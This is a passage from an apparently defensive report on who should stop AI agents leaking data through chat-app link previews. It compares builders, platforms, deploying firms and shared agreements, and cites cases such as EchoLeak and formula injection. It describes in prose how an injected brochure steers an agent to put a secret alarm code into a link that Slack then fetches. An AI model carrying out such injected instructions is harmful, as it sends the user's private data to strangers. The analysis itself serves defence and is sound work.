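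*Environment Steering* (2026), which covers rules for what data an agent may send where, helps explain the mistake. It considers a destination allowlist sufficient when the user's task names the destination, whatever the message contains, but it counts the recipient or account as part of the destination. Cowork's list checked the domain but not the account. *Environment Steering* also advises against blocking web addresses by default when the task names none, since an agent doing research has to follow links it finds. Strict egress control therefore suits an agent that files invoices much better than one that looks for new suppliers.

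### Requests the firewall never sees

The main objection to this view is that preview requests can bypass the company's firewall. In the alarm code example, Slack's servers send the request to example.com, so the firewall registers only a connection to Slack. Blocking example.com stops the office manager from opening the link at work, but the preview request has already sent the code there.

The allowlist that performed perfectly in *Silent Egress* would fail here too. An agent that answers people in Slack must be able to reach Slack, so Slack has to be on the list. But Slack will fetch an address for anyone who can post a message with link previews on, which makes it one more permitted service that an attacker can use. The same is true of Telegram.

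A company could open the agent's traffic to Slack and inspect the links before the messages leave, much as Anthropic's proxy inspects requests to its service. This would work for an agent on the company's own machines if the inspection recognised every piece of text that Slack treats as a link. EchoLeak, the attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, succeeded partly because a filter missed text that the display treated as a link. The company cannot inspect the traffic of a hosted agent that posts to Slack or opens web pages directly from its maker's servers. In Radware's attacks, the data left from OpenAI's servers, where only OpenAI could have stopped it.

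OpenAI's public-address check covers addresses that OpenAI's own software is about to fetch, so it doesn't settle the matter either. If an agent writes a link into a Slack message, Slack makes the request. OpenAI, or any other builder, could run the same check on links before posting them, but that would be a guard on the agent's output.

On this view, the platform should guard previews because it has the address before anyone fetches it. For messages from apps, Slack could adopt OpenAI's rule and preview only addresses already in a public index. A news article would still get a preview picture, but the alarm code link would not. A link to an internal support ticket would also lose its preview, unless Slack let apps register their domains. Slack would have to build an index or pay for access to one. That would be a modest burden for Slack but a larger one for a small messaging company.

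Slack can't determine whether a link came from the user, a search result or the model, but an exact-address check doesn't require that information. Until the platforms adopt such a check, a company's egress controls cover only what its agent fetches directly, and the company has to rely on the settings that turn link previews off.

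## The view that both sides share the duty under an explicit agreement

Slack and the builder already divide the work on previews, since Slack has to offer the preview settings and the builder has to turn previews off. A fourth view is that the two parties should divide the work this way for everything an app does automatically with an agent's message, and should put in writing which of them does what.

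The builder and the platform each have information the other needs. In the alarm code example, the builder can tell where the reply came from, and Slack knows which links its servers will fetch. The leak happens only if a stranger influences the link and Slack's servers fetch it automatically, and each company normally knows about only one of these conditions.

Ghosh, Simkin and colleagues (2025), from NVIDIA and the security firm Lakera, make a more general version of this argument in *A Safety and Security Framework for Real-World Agentic Systems*. They treat safety and security as properties that emerge from the way models, tools and data interact. Failures often involve several components, including user interfaces, which can make the cause hard to trace, so the researchers assess the risk of the whole system as well as that of each part. Their case study was NVIDIA's own research assistant,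 which they could run thousands of times and record from start to finish. Slack and an outside builder, by contrast, can each inspect only their own half, so each has to rely on the other for information about the rest.

PromptArmor proposed a division of this kind when it published its test of agents and messaging apps. It wanted the apps to give developers control over link previews, and agent developers to use that control or pass the choice on to users. Some press coverage put more of the responsibility on the apps, with Apostol reporting that PromptArmor considered it to lie "largely with communication platforms". That emphasis is understandable where an app has no such setting, because agent developers can't use a control that doesn't exist. Slack and Telegram already have these settings, so on those apps PromptArmor's division leaves the next step to the agent developer.

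### What the parties would have to agree

An agreement would need a label that marks a message as written by a model. The builder's ordinary code should attach it, because a prompt injection could make the model leave it out. A more detailed label could give the origin of each link, such as the user's request, a company database or the model's own text. Slack could then preview a link to a support ticket but not the brochure's link.

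The platform would supply a list of everything it does with a message before anyone clicks a link, including previews, images, notifications and email digests. If software could read the list, an agent could check it before posting and remove links from its replies when the platform added a new kind of automatic fetch.

The parties would also need a default for messages without a label. The safe choice is for the app to fetch nothing for unlabelled messages that arrive through its API. Builders would then have a practical reason to use labels, because they would need them to get link previews back. If previews were on by default, adding a label would bring no visible benefit.

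The agreement would name one party for each check. To protect the alarm code, the builder might be responsible for labelling the reply and keeping private notes out of web addresses, and Slack for not fetching links that the model wrote. The office manager's company would decide which notes the agent can read and which channels it can post in. The agreement could also include PromptArmor's suggestion of "LLM-safe channels", where previews are off, if the agent could post nowhere else.

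### Labels on bot messages

Microsoft Teams already has a label that software can read. Developers turn it on by adding the value `AIGeneratedContent` to a message, according to Microsoft's *Bot messages with AI-generated content*. The message then shows an "AI generated" tag beside the bot's name and a warning that the content may be incorrect, according to Microsoft's *Enhance AI-generated bot messages*.

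The label is for readers, and Microsoft's instructions for it don't mention link previews, so a labelled message presumably gets the same previews as any other. Teams can receive the label but has no published rule for acting on it.

A bot can also mark a Teams message as confidential, which adds a shield icon, and list up to 20 sources in separate fields, each with its own web address. Teams could use this information to skip automatic fetches for confidential messages, or to preview only the listed sources. For the confidentiality mark to work, the builder would have to base it on everything the model had read, since the visible part of a reply can be harmless.

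Slack's guidance also concentrates on readers. Slack asks developers to always tell users when content is AI-generated and, in its design advice for agents, to signal clearly when an agent acts on a user's behalf. A sentence at the bottom of a message would do this for the office manager, but a preview robot needs a fixed field that means the same thing in every message.

### Formats that limit what an agent can display

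An agreement can also be part of the message format. Google took this approach with A2UI, an open format in which an agent describes a form or a card and the app builds it from its own approved components. Google's *Introducing A2UI* emphasises that the agent sends data instead of code, so the app keeps control of styling and security.

A2UI's *v1.0 Protocol Specification* (2025) sets rules for both the agent and the app. The agent must describe its interface using a catalogue of components and functions that the app supports. The app must reject an agent's call to any function it hasn't registered. The app may open a web address only in response to a user's action, such as pressing a button, and the agent can't trigger this remotely. If neither a component nor the surface it belongs to specifies a catalogue, the app must not display the component, even if the app supports only one catalogue.

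These defaults are strict but don't cover every automatic fetch. A2UI's basic catalogue includes an image component that loads a picture from a web address. The rule about user actions applies to opening links, so an agent could put `HERON-4417` in an image's address, and the app might request that address as soon as the card appeared. Under A2UI, most finished products are expected to define their own catalogues, and a cautious platform could leave this component out. The basic catalogue's icons are safer because the agent can only choose from a fixed list.

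A2UI also has a place for extra information, such as access restrictions and audit tags, where a builder could record that a stranger's document influenced a link. But the specification requires apps to ignore any tag they don't recognise, so an app that didn't support such a warning label would display the message as usual.

The A2UI specification page lists version 1.0 as current, but in August 2026 the project page still listed it as a release candidate and 0.9.1 as the production version. The rules in version 1.0 are therefore better evidence of what developers can agree on than of what most apps do today.

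MCP Apps, an extension to the protocol many connectors use, lets a connector supply an interactive page, such as a chart or a form, for a chat app to display. Model Context Protocol (2026) acknowledges that this means "running code you didn't write". The chat app, called the host, therefore displays the page in a sandbox, a frame that isolates it from the rest of the app.

The specification, by Salomon, Yosef and colleagues (2025), in *SEP-1865*, became stable in January 2026. It comes closer to a full agreement than the others:

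1. The connector declares which outside domains its page needs for data, images and other resources.
2. The host builds a Content Security Policy from that declaration. It may be stricter than the declaration but must not permit any other domain.
3. If the connector declares nothing, the host must block all outside connections.
4. The host can tell the page which domains and permissions it has approved.

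The host also receives the page's template when it connects, so it can review the template before the agent uses the tool. A prompt injection that later arrives in a document may change the data on the page, but it ordinarily can't add a domain to the list.

Model Context Protocol's *MCP Apps Overview* claims that this default prevents data from leaking to undeclared servers. That claim is fair, but the protection is limited. A malicious connector can declare its own server, and Salomon and colleagues recommend but do not require that the host warn users about outside domains. Connectors can also declare every host under a domain with a single entry, as Salesforce's list did with amazonaws.com.

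The rules cover only what happens inside the frame. The alarm code link is in the model's reply, which the host displays as ordinary text. The Model Context Protocol site lists Claude, Microsoft 365 Copilot and several programming tools among the apps that support the extension, but not Slack or Telegram. In apps that don't support it, the connector's tool returns text, and none of these rules apply to that text.

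| Arrangement | What the agent's side does | What the displaying side does | If the information is missing | What can still leak data |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Teams AI label | Adds the label | Shows it to readers | Shows no label | Previews and images, as in any other message |
| A2UI 1.0 | Uses only components in the catalogue | Rejects unregistered functions; opens links only on a user's action | Refuses a component with no catalogue | Images, if the catalogue allows outside addresses |
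| MCP Apps | Declares the domains its page needs | Blocks all other domains | Blocks all outside connections | Declared domains that an attacker can use; the model's own text |

### The arithmetic of two guards

Sharing the duty appeals to security engineers partly because two imperfect checks can let through far fewer attacks than one. Suppose, for illustration, that the builder's check and the platform's check each miss 10% of attacks. If the failures are independent, only 1% of attacks (10% × 10%) get past both.

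Now suppose that each side leaves its check out of half of all deployments because it expects the other side to make it. If the omissions are independent, a quarter of deployments have both checks, half have one, and a quarter have none. The overall leak rate is

0.25 × 1% + 0.5 × 10% + 0.25 × 100% = 30.25%.

If the omissions coincide, half of the deployments have both checks and the other half have neither:

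0.5 × 1% + 0.5 × 100% = 50.5%.

A single check that was always present would let only 10% through. Two optional checks would do better only if each side included its own in more than about 76% of deployments, assuming the omissions were independent, or more than about 91% if both sides omitted theirs in the same deployments.

The two sides' checks probably tend to be missing together, because most people keep the defaults on both sides. OpenClaw left link previews on and Telegram fetched the links, so every user who kept the defaults had neither check.

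With the same numbers, an agreement could also reduce leaks without any extra checking. If each side still made its check in only half of the deployments, but they arranged for exactly one of them to check each time, the leak rate would be 10% in every deployment. That is two-thirds lower than if the two sides skipped checks independently, and four-fifths lower than if they skipped them in the same deployments.

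The 1% figure depends on the two checks failing independently. If both used the same filter for suspicious links, they would miss the same attacks, and 10% would still get through. The two sides would do better to check different things. The builder could look for text from private notes in the reply's web addresses, and the platform could decline to fetch the links at all.

OpenAI uses layers in this way, combining its check on web addresses with model training, product controls and monitoring. But OpenAI runs all of those layers itself, so it can find out when one is missing, whereas a builder and a platform that divide the layers between them would have to tell each other.

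### Relying on the other side

Critics can reasonably object that a shared duty encourages the omissions in the calculation. A developer who knows that Slack also checks links has less reason to spend a week on a filter. An agreement that merely made both parties responsible for safety could increase the leak rate by giving each an excuse to rely on the other.

This is a good argument against vague agreements. Under a specific one, the developer would know which check Slack makes and which it leaves to them. The parties also need a way to find out whether the checks exist. The Model Context Protocol working group responsible for MCP Apps describes its job as standardising a "security contract". One of its goals is a set of tests to verify that hosts apply the required sandboxing and content policies. The group leaves individual apps to their developers, so a host that passed every test could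 still display an app that declared a carelessly chosen list of domains.

### Missing and false labels

Microsoft's *Best Practices* only recommends the Teams label, and a label can be missing even when a builder has tried to add it. In January, mj2148 (2026) reported in *AI content label is not appearing when using Microsoft botbuilder Typescript library* that they had copied Microsoft's sample code exactly and got no label. One report doesn't show how common the problem is, but it shows why a platform shouldn't treat an unlabelled message as safe. With previews off by default, the same fault would have left the user without a preview picture and leaked nothing.

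False labels are harder to deal with. A builder who wants attractive previews could mark every link as coming from a trusted database. A platform could limit the damage by previewing labelled links only if they point to domains the app had registered. A malicious builder whose agent can already read the company's notes often has easier ways to steal them than a link preview, so labels are mainly useful between honest parties that don't know enough about each other's software.

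Like a platform's rule for bots, labels don't cover messages that an agent or its user posts through a person's account.

### Builders who won't read the agreement

Many connectors are built by one person over a weekend, who is unlikely to study a long specification before posting a message to Slack. Even a careful reader may have trouble, because published instructions conflict. Salomon and colleagues require a web host to serve the outer frame around an MCP App from a different origin, which in practice usually means a different domain. In the guide to displaying MCP Apps inside A2UI, the host serves that frame from its own origin and relies on tighter restrictions on the frame inside it. A2UI's design may be safe, but a developer who follows it doesn't meet the MCP Apps requirement.

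The usual remedy is to put the agreement into the software that builders already use. Microsoft's current toolkit for Teams automatically adds the AI label to replies that go through its AI module. The MCP Apps toolkit has a component that handles the sandbox and enforces the security policy for the host. A builder who uses these tools follows much of the agreement without reading it. For AG-UI, a protocol that carries messages between agents and interfaces, Microsoft recommends a similar default for data sent from the interface to the agent, advising developers to reject any field they don't expect.

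Toolkits don't help with software that nobody updates. Anthropic's abandoned Slack connector, for example, will never add a label, so only the default for unlabelled messages would protect its users.

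## Knowledge, control, cost and incentives as tests of who should guard

The four views disagree partly because their supporters ask different questions. People who hold the builder responsible tend to ask who knows that a link is dangerous, and people who want the guard at the fetch ask who controls the request. The case for the platform depends heavily on cost, because one new default would protect every old connector. Supporters of an agreement worry about incentives, because either party may do nothing and hope the other acts. Each question has a classic answer from computer science, law or political theory, but these answers came with conditions, and a preview leak doesn't meet all of those conditions.

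### Knowledge: who can recognise a dangerous link

*End-to-End Arguments in System Design* (Saltzer, Reed and Clark, 1984) considers which jobs a network should do and which it should leave to the programs that use it. According to its "end-to-end argument", the network can't fully do a job on its own if the job needs the knowledge of the programs at either end, although it may do part of the job to improve performance.

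Suppose a program copies a file from one computer to another. The network can check every packet, but a disk may misread the file before it is sent, or the software at either end may garble it. The receiving program therefore has to read back its stored copy, calculate a checksum (a short number derived from the file's contents) and send this to the sending program, which compares it with the original file's checksum. Once the programs do this, a more reliable network saves some retries but doesn't make the final copy more accurate.

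A network at MIT showed what can happen without the final check. It checked each packet between one gateway and the next, and programmers who knew this assumed that their data arrived intact. But nothing protected the data while a gateway was storing it, and one faulty gateway swapped a pair of bytes about once in every million bytes. This corrupted some of an operating system's source files, and their owners had to compare them by hand with old listings. The programmers had relied on a check without knowing what it didn't cover, much as a builder may assume that Slack has made its previews safe.

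With link previews, the builder can tell what is private, and Slack knows what it will fetch. It is easier for the builder to learn what Slack knows than the reverse, because Slack can describe its previews once for all builders. If Slack did the checking, a builder would have to tell it which text was secret or get it to trust a label on each link.

Even the builder's knowledge is incomplete. The builder's software records the notes the model read, but a search for the original text would miss the code if the model reversed it or turned it into numbers before putting it in an address. It may be impossible to separate every bad link from every good one. Fetching no links is cruder, but nobody has to recognise the secret for it to work, so either side can do it.

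Saltzer and colleagues warn that designers must identify the ends carefully. If the ends are the agent and the office manager, Slack is in the middle, and link previews are the kind of extra help the paper advises against adding there. But Slack's server is also one end of the request to example.com. The right design can also change with the use. In a live phone call, the network shouldn't delay the conversation to resend a damaged packet, because the listener can ask the speaker to repeat a word. The listener to a recorded message can't ask, so accuracy matters more, and a short delay does no harm. A platform could likewise have good reason to fetch a colleague's link and not an agent's, although the two links look the same.

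The paper's treatment of encryption weakens the case for leaving everything to the builder. Under the end-to-end argument, programs that need secrecy should encrypt their own data. But Saltzer and colleagues accept that a network may also encrypt all traffic automatically, to stop a misbehaving user or program from deliberately sending out information. An agent under prompt injection is a misbehaving program at one of the ends, so a guard that depends on that end behaving well needs a backup.

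### Control: whose authority the request uses

In *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975), Saltzer and Schroeder set out eight design principles that security courses still teach. One of them, complete mediation, requires a system to check that every access to every object is authorized. They point out that this check needs a foolproof way to identify the source of each request.

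When Slack previews a link, the attacker's server receives a request from Slack's robot, Slack has a message from the connector, and the connector has a reply from the model. None of them has a record that a paragraph in the brochure supplied the address. Saltzer and Schroeder were also wary of systems that remember the result of an earlier check, because permissions can change in the meantime. A Slack administrator approves a connector once, and that approval covers every message it posts, including any that a stranger has influenced.

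Their principle of fail-safe defaults applies almost directly to previews. Access should be denied unless there is a reason to allow it, partly because mistakes are then easier to notice. If an app fetches only permitted links, a mistake in the settings makes a preview disappear, and a user will probably complain. If it fetches everything that isn't excluded, a mistake lets a request through and the message looks normal. Anthropic's Slack connector failed silently in this way.

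Another principle counts against having central preview services at all. Saltzer and Schroeder advise designers to minimise the machinery that all users share, because information can pass between users through it. Slack's preview robot serves every customer and will visit a stranger's server for any of them. A builder who wants a title under a link can often include it in the message as text, so no shared robot has to visit the page.

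*LLM Agents Should Employ Security Principles* (Zhang, Su and colleagues, 2025) applies several of these principles in a design called AgentSandbox. A persistent agent keeps the user's personal information, and a temporary agent does each task and then disappears. One component gives the temporary agent only the data its task requires. Another checks every message between that agent and the outside world.

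In the alarm code example, the restriction on data would be the more useful part. Summarising a brochure doesn't require the alarm code, so the temporary agent should never receive it, and an injection then couldn't make the agent send it. Checking the outgoing message would help only if the check took account of Slack's previews. Zhang and colleagues assume that the defender has full control over the agent's design, which is true of a builder but not of a company that installs a finished connector. Even a builder doesn't control what Slack does with a message after the agent has sent it.

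### The confused deputy

Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* describes an incident that helps explain why the platform's own code can be correct and still leak. Tymshare, which sold time on its computers in the 1970s, had a compiler, a program that turns other programs into a form the computer can run. Tymshare let the compiler write files in the compiler's own directory so that it could keep usage statistics there. The company's billing records were in the same directory.

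Users could tell the compiler where to save its debugging output, and one of them entered the name of the billing file. The user probably had no right to change that file, but the compiler did, and it overwrote the bills. Hardy doesn't blame the output code, which was correct when the programmers wrote it but became wrong when Tymshare gave the compiler the extra permission. The compiler was a "confused deputy" because it had authority from both the user and Tymshare and no way to keep the two apart.

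Slack's preview robot is a deputy of the same kind. It uses Slack's network access to fetch whatever address the message's author supplies, so an agent that the company's firewall blocks from example.com can post a link and have Slack contact the site instead. The robot's code was reasonable when people chose the links. It became dangerous in a particular workspace when someone connected an agent there, even though the code had not changed.

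Lan and colleagues apply the same idea to an agent that misuses its tools by following a web page's instructions. They distinguish the agent from Hardy's compiler, which had authority from two sources, because the agent is confused about what its user intended. A preview leak can involve both kinds of confusion. The model mistakes the brochure's instruction for part of the job, and the robot then treats the model's link as one that a person wanted to share.

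Tymshare first tried a command that let a program choose which of its authorities to use. Some programs soon needed more than two authorities, and the changes spread through the system. Hardy preferred capabilities, which are references that both identify a file and give permission to use it. The user would have given the compiler a capability for the output file instead of typing its name. A user without permission to write to the billing file could not have given the compiler a capability to do so.

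For previews, a label on each link could work like a capability if only the builder's ordinary code could attach it and Slack fetched no link without it. This also fits Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of separation of privilege, under which access requires two keys held by separate parties.

The builder would need a reliable way to decide which links get the label. Lan and colleagues suggest taint tracking, in which software marks text from outside, and anything that text influences, as tainted. The software can then block a tainted request or ask the user about it, even if the request contains only a harmless-looking fragment of a secret. But a summary of the supplier's brochure is entirely tainted, so every link the model wrote in it would lose its preview, including the one to the supplier's real home page. The builder would have to accept this small loss for the method to work.

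Slack controls link previews, which is a reason for Slack to guard them, with the builder telling it about possible exceptions. When the agent opens a page itself, whoever runs the agent's machine has that control, and the same reasoning applies to them.

### Cost: who can prevent the leak most cheaply

Guido Calabresi, an American legal scholar, changed how lawyers think about accidents with a book published in 1970. Coleman (2005) writes in *The Costs of The Costs of Accidents* that lawyers had mostly asked whether one person should compensate another for a particular harm. Calabresi asked what society should do about accidents in general, and aimed to minimise the combined cost of accidents and their prevention. By that standard, a precaution isn't worth taking if it costs more than the harm it prevents.

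The cheapest cost avoider is the party who could have prevented an accident at the lowest cost. Calabresi and Hirschoff turned this idea into a legal test in 1972. Pardolesi and Tassone explain in *Guido Calabresi on Torts* that a court would ask which party was best placed to compare the cost of accidents with the cost of avoiding them, and to act on the result. The court wouldn't have to decide whether anyone should have prevented the injury.

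Pardolesi and Tassone describe a case from a court in Venice in which a schoolgirl fell against the glass wall of a gym during a lesson, and her parents sued the education ministry. In 2003 the court placed the cost on the party best able to control the risk and invest in precautions. It observed that the girl could have taken no precaution, except perhaps to give up gymnastics. A company that can't change its connector or Slack's preview service is in a similar position, because it may have to give up the agent to be safe.

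Suppose 20 agents each post to the same five platforms. If the builders have to turn previews off, they must configure 20 × 5 = 100 agent-platform pairs, whereas the platforms could change their defaults with five changes in total. A twenty-first agent would add five pairs for its builder to configure but no work for the platforms.

The comparison of 100 with five understates the platforms' work, because each platform has more to do than each builder. A builder might need two hours to add and test the settings. A platform has to warn developers, rewrite its documentation and handle complaints, which might take 100 hours. Harmless bots also lose their previews under the new default. If each platform has 300 such bots and restoring the previews takes each developer an hour, that adds 1,500 hours across the five platforms. All these figures are invented to show which quantities matter.

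| | Builders configure each pairing | Platforms change the default |
|---|---|---|
| Changes needed | 100 | 5 |
| Hours per change | 2 | 100 |
| Hours spent on the changes | 200 | 500 |
| Hours spent restoring harmless bots' previews | 0 | 1,500 |
| Total hours | 200 | 2,000 |

Precautions would take the builders a tenth of the hours they would take the platforms, but these totals leave out losses from leaks. If the builders miss a fifth of the pairings, 20 remain exposed, and the platforms would need an extra 1,800 hours to protect them. The new default is then worth the extra work if an exposed pairing would, on average, cause losses equal to more than 90 hours of work over its lifetime (1,800 ÷ 20). Losses could easily exceed that for an agent with thousands of business customers, but probably wouldn't for a hobbyist's bot with two users.

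The platforms could also reduce the time spent restoring previews, which is the largest item. For simple bots that link to only a few sites, a platform could use its own logs to approve those sites in advance. If four-fifths of the harmless bots kept their previews this way without any work by their developers, the time needed to restore the rest would fall to 300 hours and the platforms' total to 800. Each exposed pairing would then need to cause losses worth only 30 hours. The estimate excludes the work of searching the logs and the loss to readers when an unmaintained bot never gets its previews back.

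Leaving the work to deploying organisations would probably cost the most. If each of the 20 agents had 50 business customers, up to 1,000 companies would have to learn about the same danger. Some would guard against it badly, and none could stop Slack's fetch with their egress controls.

Calabresi and Hirschoff's test also depends on who can make the comparison. Slack could count how many bot messages contain links and how many of those links readers open. Builders know more about the value of the data their agents can read. Neither can make the comparison alone, but Slack has the figures on harmless previews, which affect the answer most.

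An inexpensive fix may still be unfair. The developer of a ticket bot would lose an hour, and perhaps some attractive previews, because other people had connected unreliable agents to the same app. Coleman considers the treatment of fairness the weakest part of Calabresi's book, and also objects in general to treating costs as what matters most about accidents, since some also involve wrongs or violations of rights. A careless builder may deserve more blame than Slack even if Slack can fix the problem at lower cost. Slack could change its default without accepting that blame, and a builder who had ignored a clear warning could still owe the victim something.

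### Incentives: who loses if nobody acts

The company whose alarm code leaks has the strongest reason to prevent it, but it often controls neither the connector's code nor Slack's preview robot. The builder and Slack control those components and lose much less from a leak, which may damage their reputations but doesn't give the attacker access to their warehouses.

The problem of many hands makes it harder to put pressure on either of them. The political theorist Dennis Thompson named the problem in a 1980 article on the responsibility of public officials. Helen Nissenbaum applied it to computing in 1996 and listed three other obstacles to accountability: accepting bugs as inevitable, blaming the computer, and owning software without accepting liability for it. Similarly, it is now easy to say, correctly, that the model followed an injected instruction and forget that a person chose to leave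 previews on.

The "problem of many hands" can mean that nobody can assign blame after a failure or that nobody took on the job of preventing it. *The Problem of Many Hands* distinguishes backward-looking from forward-looking responsibility. The forward-looking kind matters more here, because investigators can reconstruct a preview leak from a few logs but would find it harder to show that any of the companies involved had agreed in advance to prevent it.

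Blame may then fall on whoever was nearest to the failure. Madeleine Elish calls this a "moral crumple zone", after the part of a car that absorbs the force of a crash. An article on AIhub, a website about AI research, adds that people in this position do unnoticed work that prevents failures, and that the AI gets the credit for it. In the alarm code example, the blame would probably fall on the administrator who installed the connector or the office manager who asked for the summary. If the administrator had found the preview setting and turned it off, the code would not have leaked, and nobody would have noticed that work.

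The threat of having to pay can also fail to make parties take care if they don't know who will pay. Dari-Mattiacci and Garoupa (2007), in *Least-Cost Avoidance*, study accidents that either of two parties could prevent, such as a collision between a diver and a swimmer. Only one needs to take care, and it is cheapest if the one with the lower cost does so. But if neither knows the other's cost, neither can predict whom a court will hold responsible. Any care that one takes also protects the other from liability, so both take too little, a result Dari-Mattiacci and Garoupa call "the tragedy of common safety".

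Suppose leaks will cause $10,000 of harm a year, and either the builder or the platform could prevent them all for $6,000. The precaution is worth taking. But if each party thinks it has an even chance of having to pay for the harm, each expects to save only $5,000 by acting. Neither will spend $6,000 to save $5,000, so the leaks continue.

Dari-Mattiacci and Garoupa show that fines for failing to take a required precaution would remove this problem, because a party would pay for its own omission whether or not an accident followed. Another solution is to let the party that takes care recover its costs from the other. Their model assumes strangers who cannot make an agreement, like drivers about to collide. Slack and a builder can make one, since Slack publishes rules for developers and can change them. This supports dividing the work in writing, provided someone can check whether each party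 has done its part.

On incentives alone, a platform with paying business customers may be a better guard than the developer of a free connector, who may have no contract with those customers and can stop maintaining the software. A commercial agent builder has incentives closer to the platform's. But the platform has a reason to keep previews, because users would notice if they disappeared and very few will notice a leak. Customers could change that incentive by asking about previews before they buy.

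### Formula injection: exporters and spreadsheet makers

Many web services let users export a table as a CSV file, which is plain text with commas between the cells. Spreadsheet programs treat a cell that begins with an equals sign as a formula. In formula injection, also known as CSV injection, an attacker puts a formula in the name field of a sign-up form and waits for an employee to export the list and open it. Some formulas could start other programs on the employee's computer. Others build a web link from the surrounding cells, and clicking it sends those cells' contents to the attacker, much like the alarm code link.

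The security researcher James Kettle drew attention to the problem in a 2014 article, *Comma Separated Vulnerabilities*. Exporters could reply that their files contained only text. Google took this position in its bug bounty rules, which assign the fix to the program that opens the file. Microsoft regarded formulas as a normal feature of Excel and relied on warnings before anything dangerous ran, so exporters who didn't trust their users to read the warnings had to remove the formulas themselves.

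Knowledge was split as it was with previews. An exporter can tell which cells came from strangers, but each spreadsheet program has its own rules about what counts as a formula. Cells that begin with a plus, minus or at sign can also be risky. OWASP advises exporters to start such cells with a single quotation mark, but warns that no single method is safe for every program. The quotation mark can spoil legitimate data, such as a negative number or a phone number that begins with a plus, when other software reads the file.

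Control and cost both favour giving the job of guarding to the spreadsheet makers. Their programs run the formulas, and a few such programs open files from a huge number of exporters. Makers and exporters both have less incentive to guard, because the person who opens the file bears most of the harm.

Nobody coordinated the reports, so there is no reliable count of the companies that researchers notified or that made a fix. In August 2014, Apache OpenOffice 4.1.1 fixed a flaw that let a spreadsheet run commands (CVE-2014-3524). Microsoft later turned off by default the old Excel feature that let a cell start another program. Both changes were made in the spreadsheet program, the layer favoured by the control and cost tests, but they dealt only with the worst formulas, and ordinary formulas still worked. Meanwhile, many exporters added filters, one product at a time. The catalogue of software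 weaknesses describes the problem, in entry CWE-1236, as a failure by the program that writes the file.

The result was two partial safeguards and a long argument, and neither Slack nor the builder seems likely to concede soon. But the outcome does suggest that a platform can remove the most dangerous automatic behaviour without first agreeing with every sender about who is to blame.

### Trojan Source: code that people and compilers read differently

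Nicholas Boucher and Ross Anderson of the University of Cambridge described a similar split in *Trojan Source* (2021). Unicode, the standard for computer text, includes invisible characters that control the direction of writing, which people need when they mix Arabic or Hebrew with English. An attacker can place these characters in a program's comments so that an editor displays the code in a different order from the one the compiler uses. A reviewer may then see a security check that the compiler treats as a comment. Boucher and Anderson made the attack work in several languages, including C, Java, Python, Rust and Go.

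The compiler, the editor and the website that hosts the code could each have prevented the deception. Boucher and Anderson notified 19 software suppliers and kept the discovery secret for 99 days. All 19 confirmed receipt, and nine committed to releasing a patch. Eleven of the suppliers offered payment for reports of flaws, and five of those paid.

The suppliers that acted put defences in different layers. Rust released version 1.56.1 on the day of publication, 1 November 2021, and its compiler now rejects the suspicious characters in comments and text unless the programmer allows them. GCC 12, released the following year, added a compiler warning. GitHub began showing a warning above files that contain the characters. Russ Cox, who led work on the Go language at Google, argued against changing compilers and preferred defences in editors and code review tools, where the characters mislead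 the reader.

The knowledge test partly supports Cox, because the display software determines what the reviewer sees. But the compiler has the other half of the information, the order in which the code will run. The control test favours the compiler, which can reject a suspicious program whichever editor the reviewer used. The cost test favours compilers and the main hosting sites, because there are few of them compared with the programmers who depend on them. The incentives test doesn't clearly favour any of these tools, because a company that runs the finished software may control none of them. The layers that acted were therefore reasonable choices, though the tests support more than one layer. Ten of the 19 suppliers hadn't committed to a patch.

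Rust's developers also measured what a stricter default would break. They searched every version of every package published on Rust's public registry up to 17 October 2021 and found the characters in only five packages, none of them malicious. Slack or Telegram could similarly count the bots whose messages include previews before changing a default. They would certainly find far more than five, since previews are much more common than these characters, but the count would replace the invented 300 in the cost example with a real number.

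### Where the tests conflict

Builders know more of what a guard needs to keep good previews and block bad ones, while the platform has more control over the request itself. Which of them should guard on grounds of cost depends on how many pairings builders miss and how many harmless previews a new default would remove, though abandoned connectors strengthen the case for the platform. The deploying organisation has the strongest incentive to guard but the least power over a preview.

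The conflict is smaller for a simple rule against fetching links from bots by default. The platform can apply the rule without knowing what is secret, and the builder can supply that knowledge later when asking for an exception. Egress control does well on incentives because the company is protecting its own data, but that doesn't make up for its lack of control over link previews.

| Test | Builder turns previews off | Platform fetches nothing for bots by default | Deploying organisation uses egress control | Written agreement between builder and platform |
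|---|---|---|---|---|
| Knowledge | Good: the builder can tell what the model read | Enough to block every fetch, but not to judge a link | Poor for previews: the company's firewall registers only a connection to Slack | Best: combines what both sides know |
| Control | Indirect: works through the platform's settings | Strong: the platform's servers make the request | Strong for the agent's own fetches, none for Slack's | Strong if the platform refuses to fetch unlabelled links |
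| Cost | Low for each pairing, but every builder has to do it | Few changes, plus the previews that harmless bots lose | High in total, because every customer repeats the work | High at first, since the parties need a common format and tests |
| Incentives | Weak for free or abandoned connectors | Mixed: customers want safety and also like previews | Strong: the company's own data is at risk | Better than relying on each other, if someone checks the work |

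## How vulnerability reports, contracts and law assign the duty today

When a researcher reports a preview leak, somebody has to decide whose flaw it is, even if the builder and the platform disagree about who should have prevented it. That decision is often first made in the CVE (Common Vulnerabilities and Exposures) catalogue. A company that pays for such reports through a bug bounty also has to decide whether the flaw qualifies. Contracts and law usually matter later, once someone has suffered a loss.

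### Why a CVE record names a product

The CVE Program's *CVE Numbering Authority (CNA) Operational Rules* (2026), in force since 25 August, define a vulnerability as a weakness in a product that someone can exploit to harm confidentiality, integrity or availability. A CVE record must describe the flaw, state its type or cause, link to a public source, and name at least one product that is or may be affected. CNAs, the organisations that issue CVE numbers, are often the products' own suppliers.

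The name matters because companies search the catalogue for software they have installed, and they can't easily look up "an agent connected to a chat app".

A vulnerability record may name several products, so a record for a preview leak could list both the connector and Slack. But if a product is vulnerable because of how it uses another product's function, and there is a secure way to use that function, the rules require a separate record for each product that uses it insecurely. Slack's previews can be used securely because a builder can turn them off. Twenty connectors that leave previews on and share no code would therefore get 20 records, each naming a connector.

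If Slack had no such settings, the same rule would require a single number for the whole problem, and Slack would be the obvious product to name. So a platform can keep its name off these records by offering a setting to turn previews off, even if they are on by default.

The default itself could still count as a vulnerability. CVE Numbering Authorities (CNAs) should treat an insecure default as a vulnerability if it is surprising, poorly documented or directly exploitable, but they may make an exception for one that is widely known and consistently well documented. Slack could make a fair case for this exception, although its guide is inconsistent about what happens when a builder sets neither option. OpenClaw's case is weaker because its Telegram guide has only two sentences on previews. The CVE Program expects disputes over defaults and advises a CNA that can't reach a clear decision to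 issue a CVE number.

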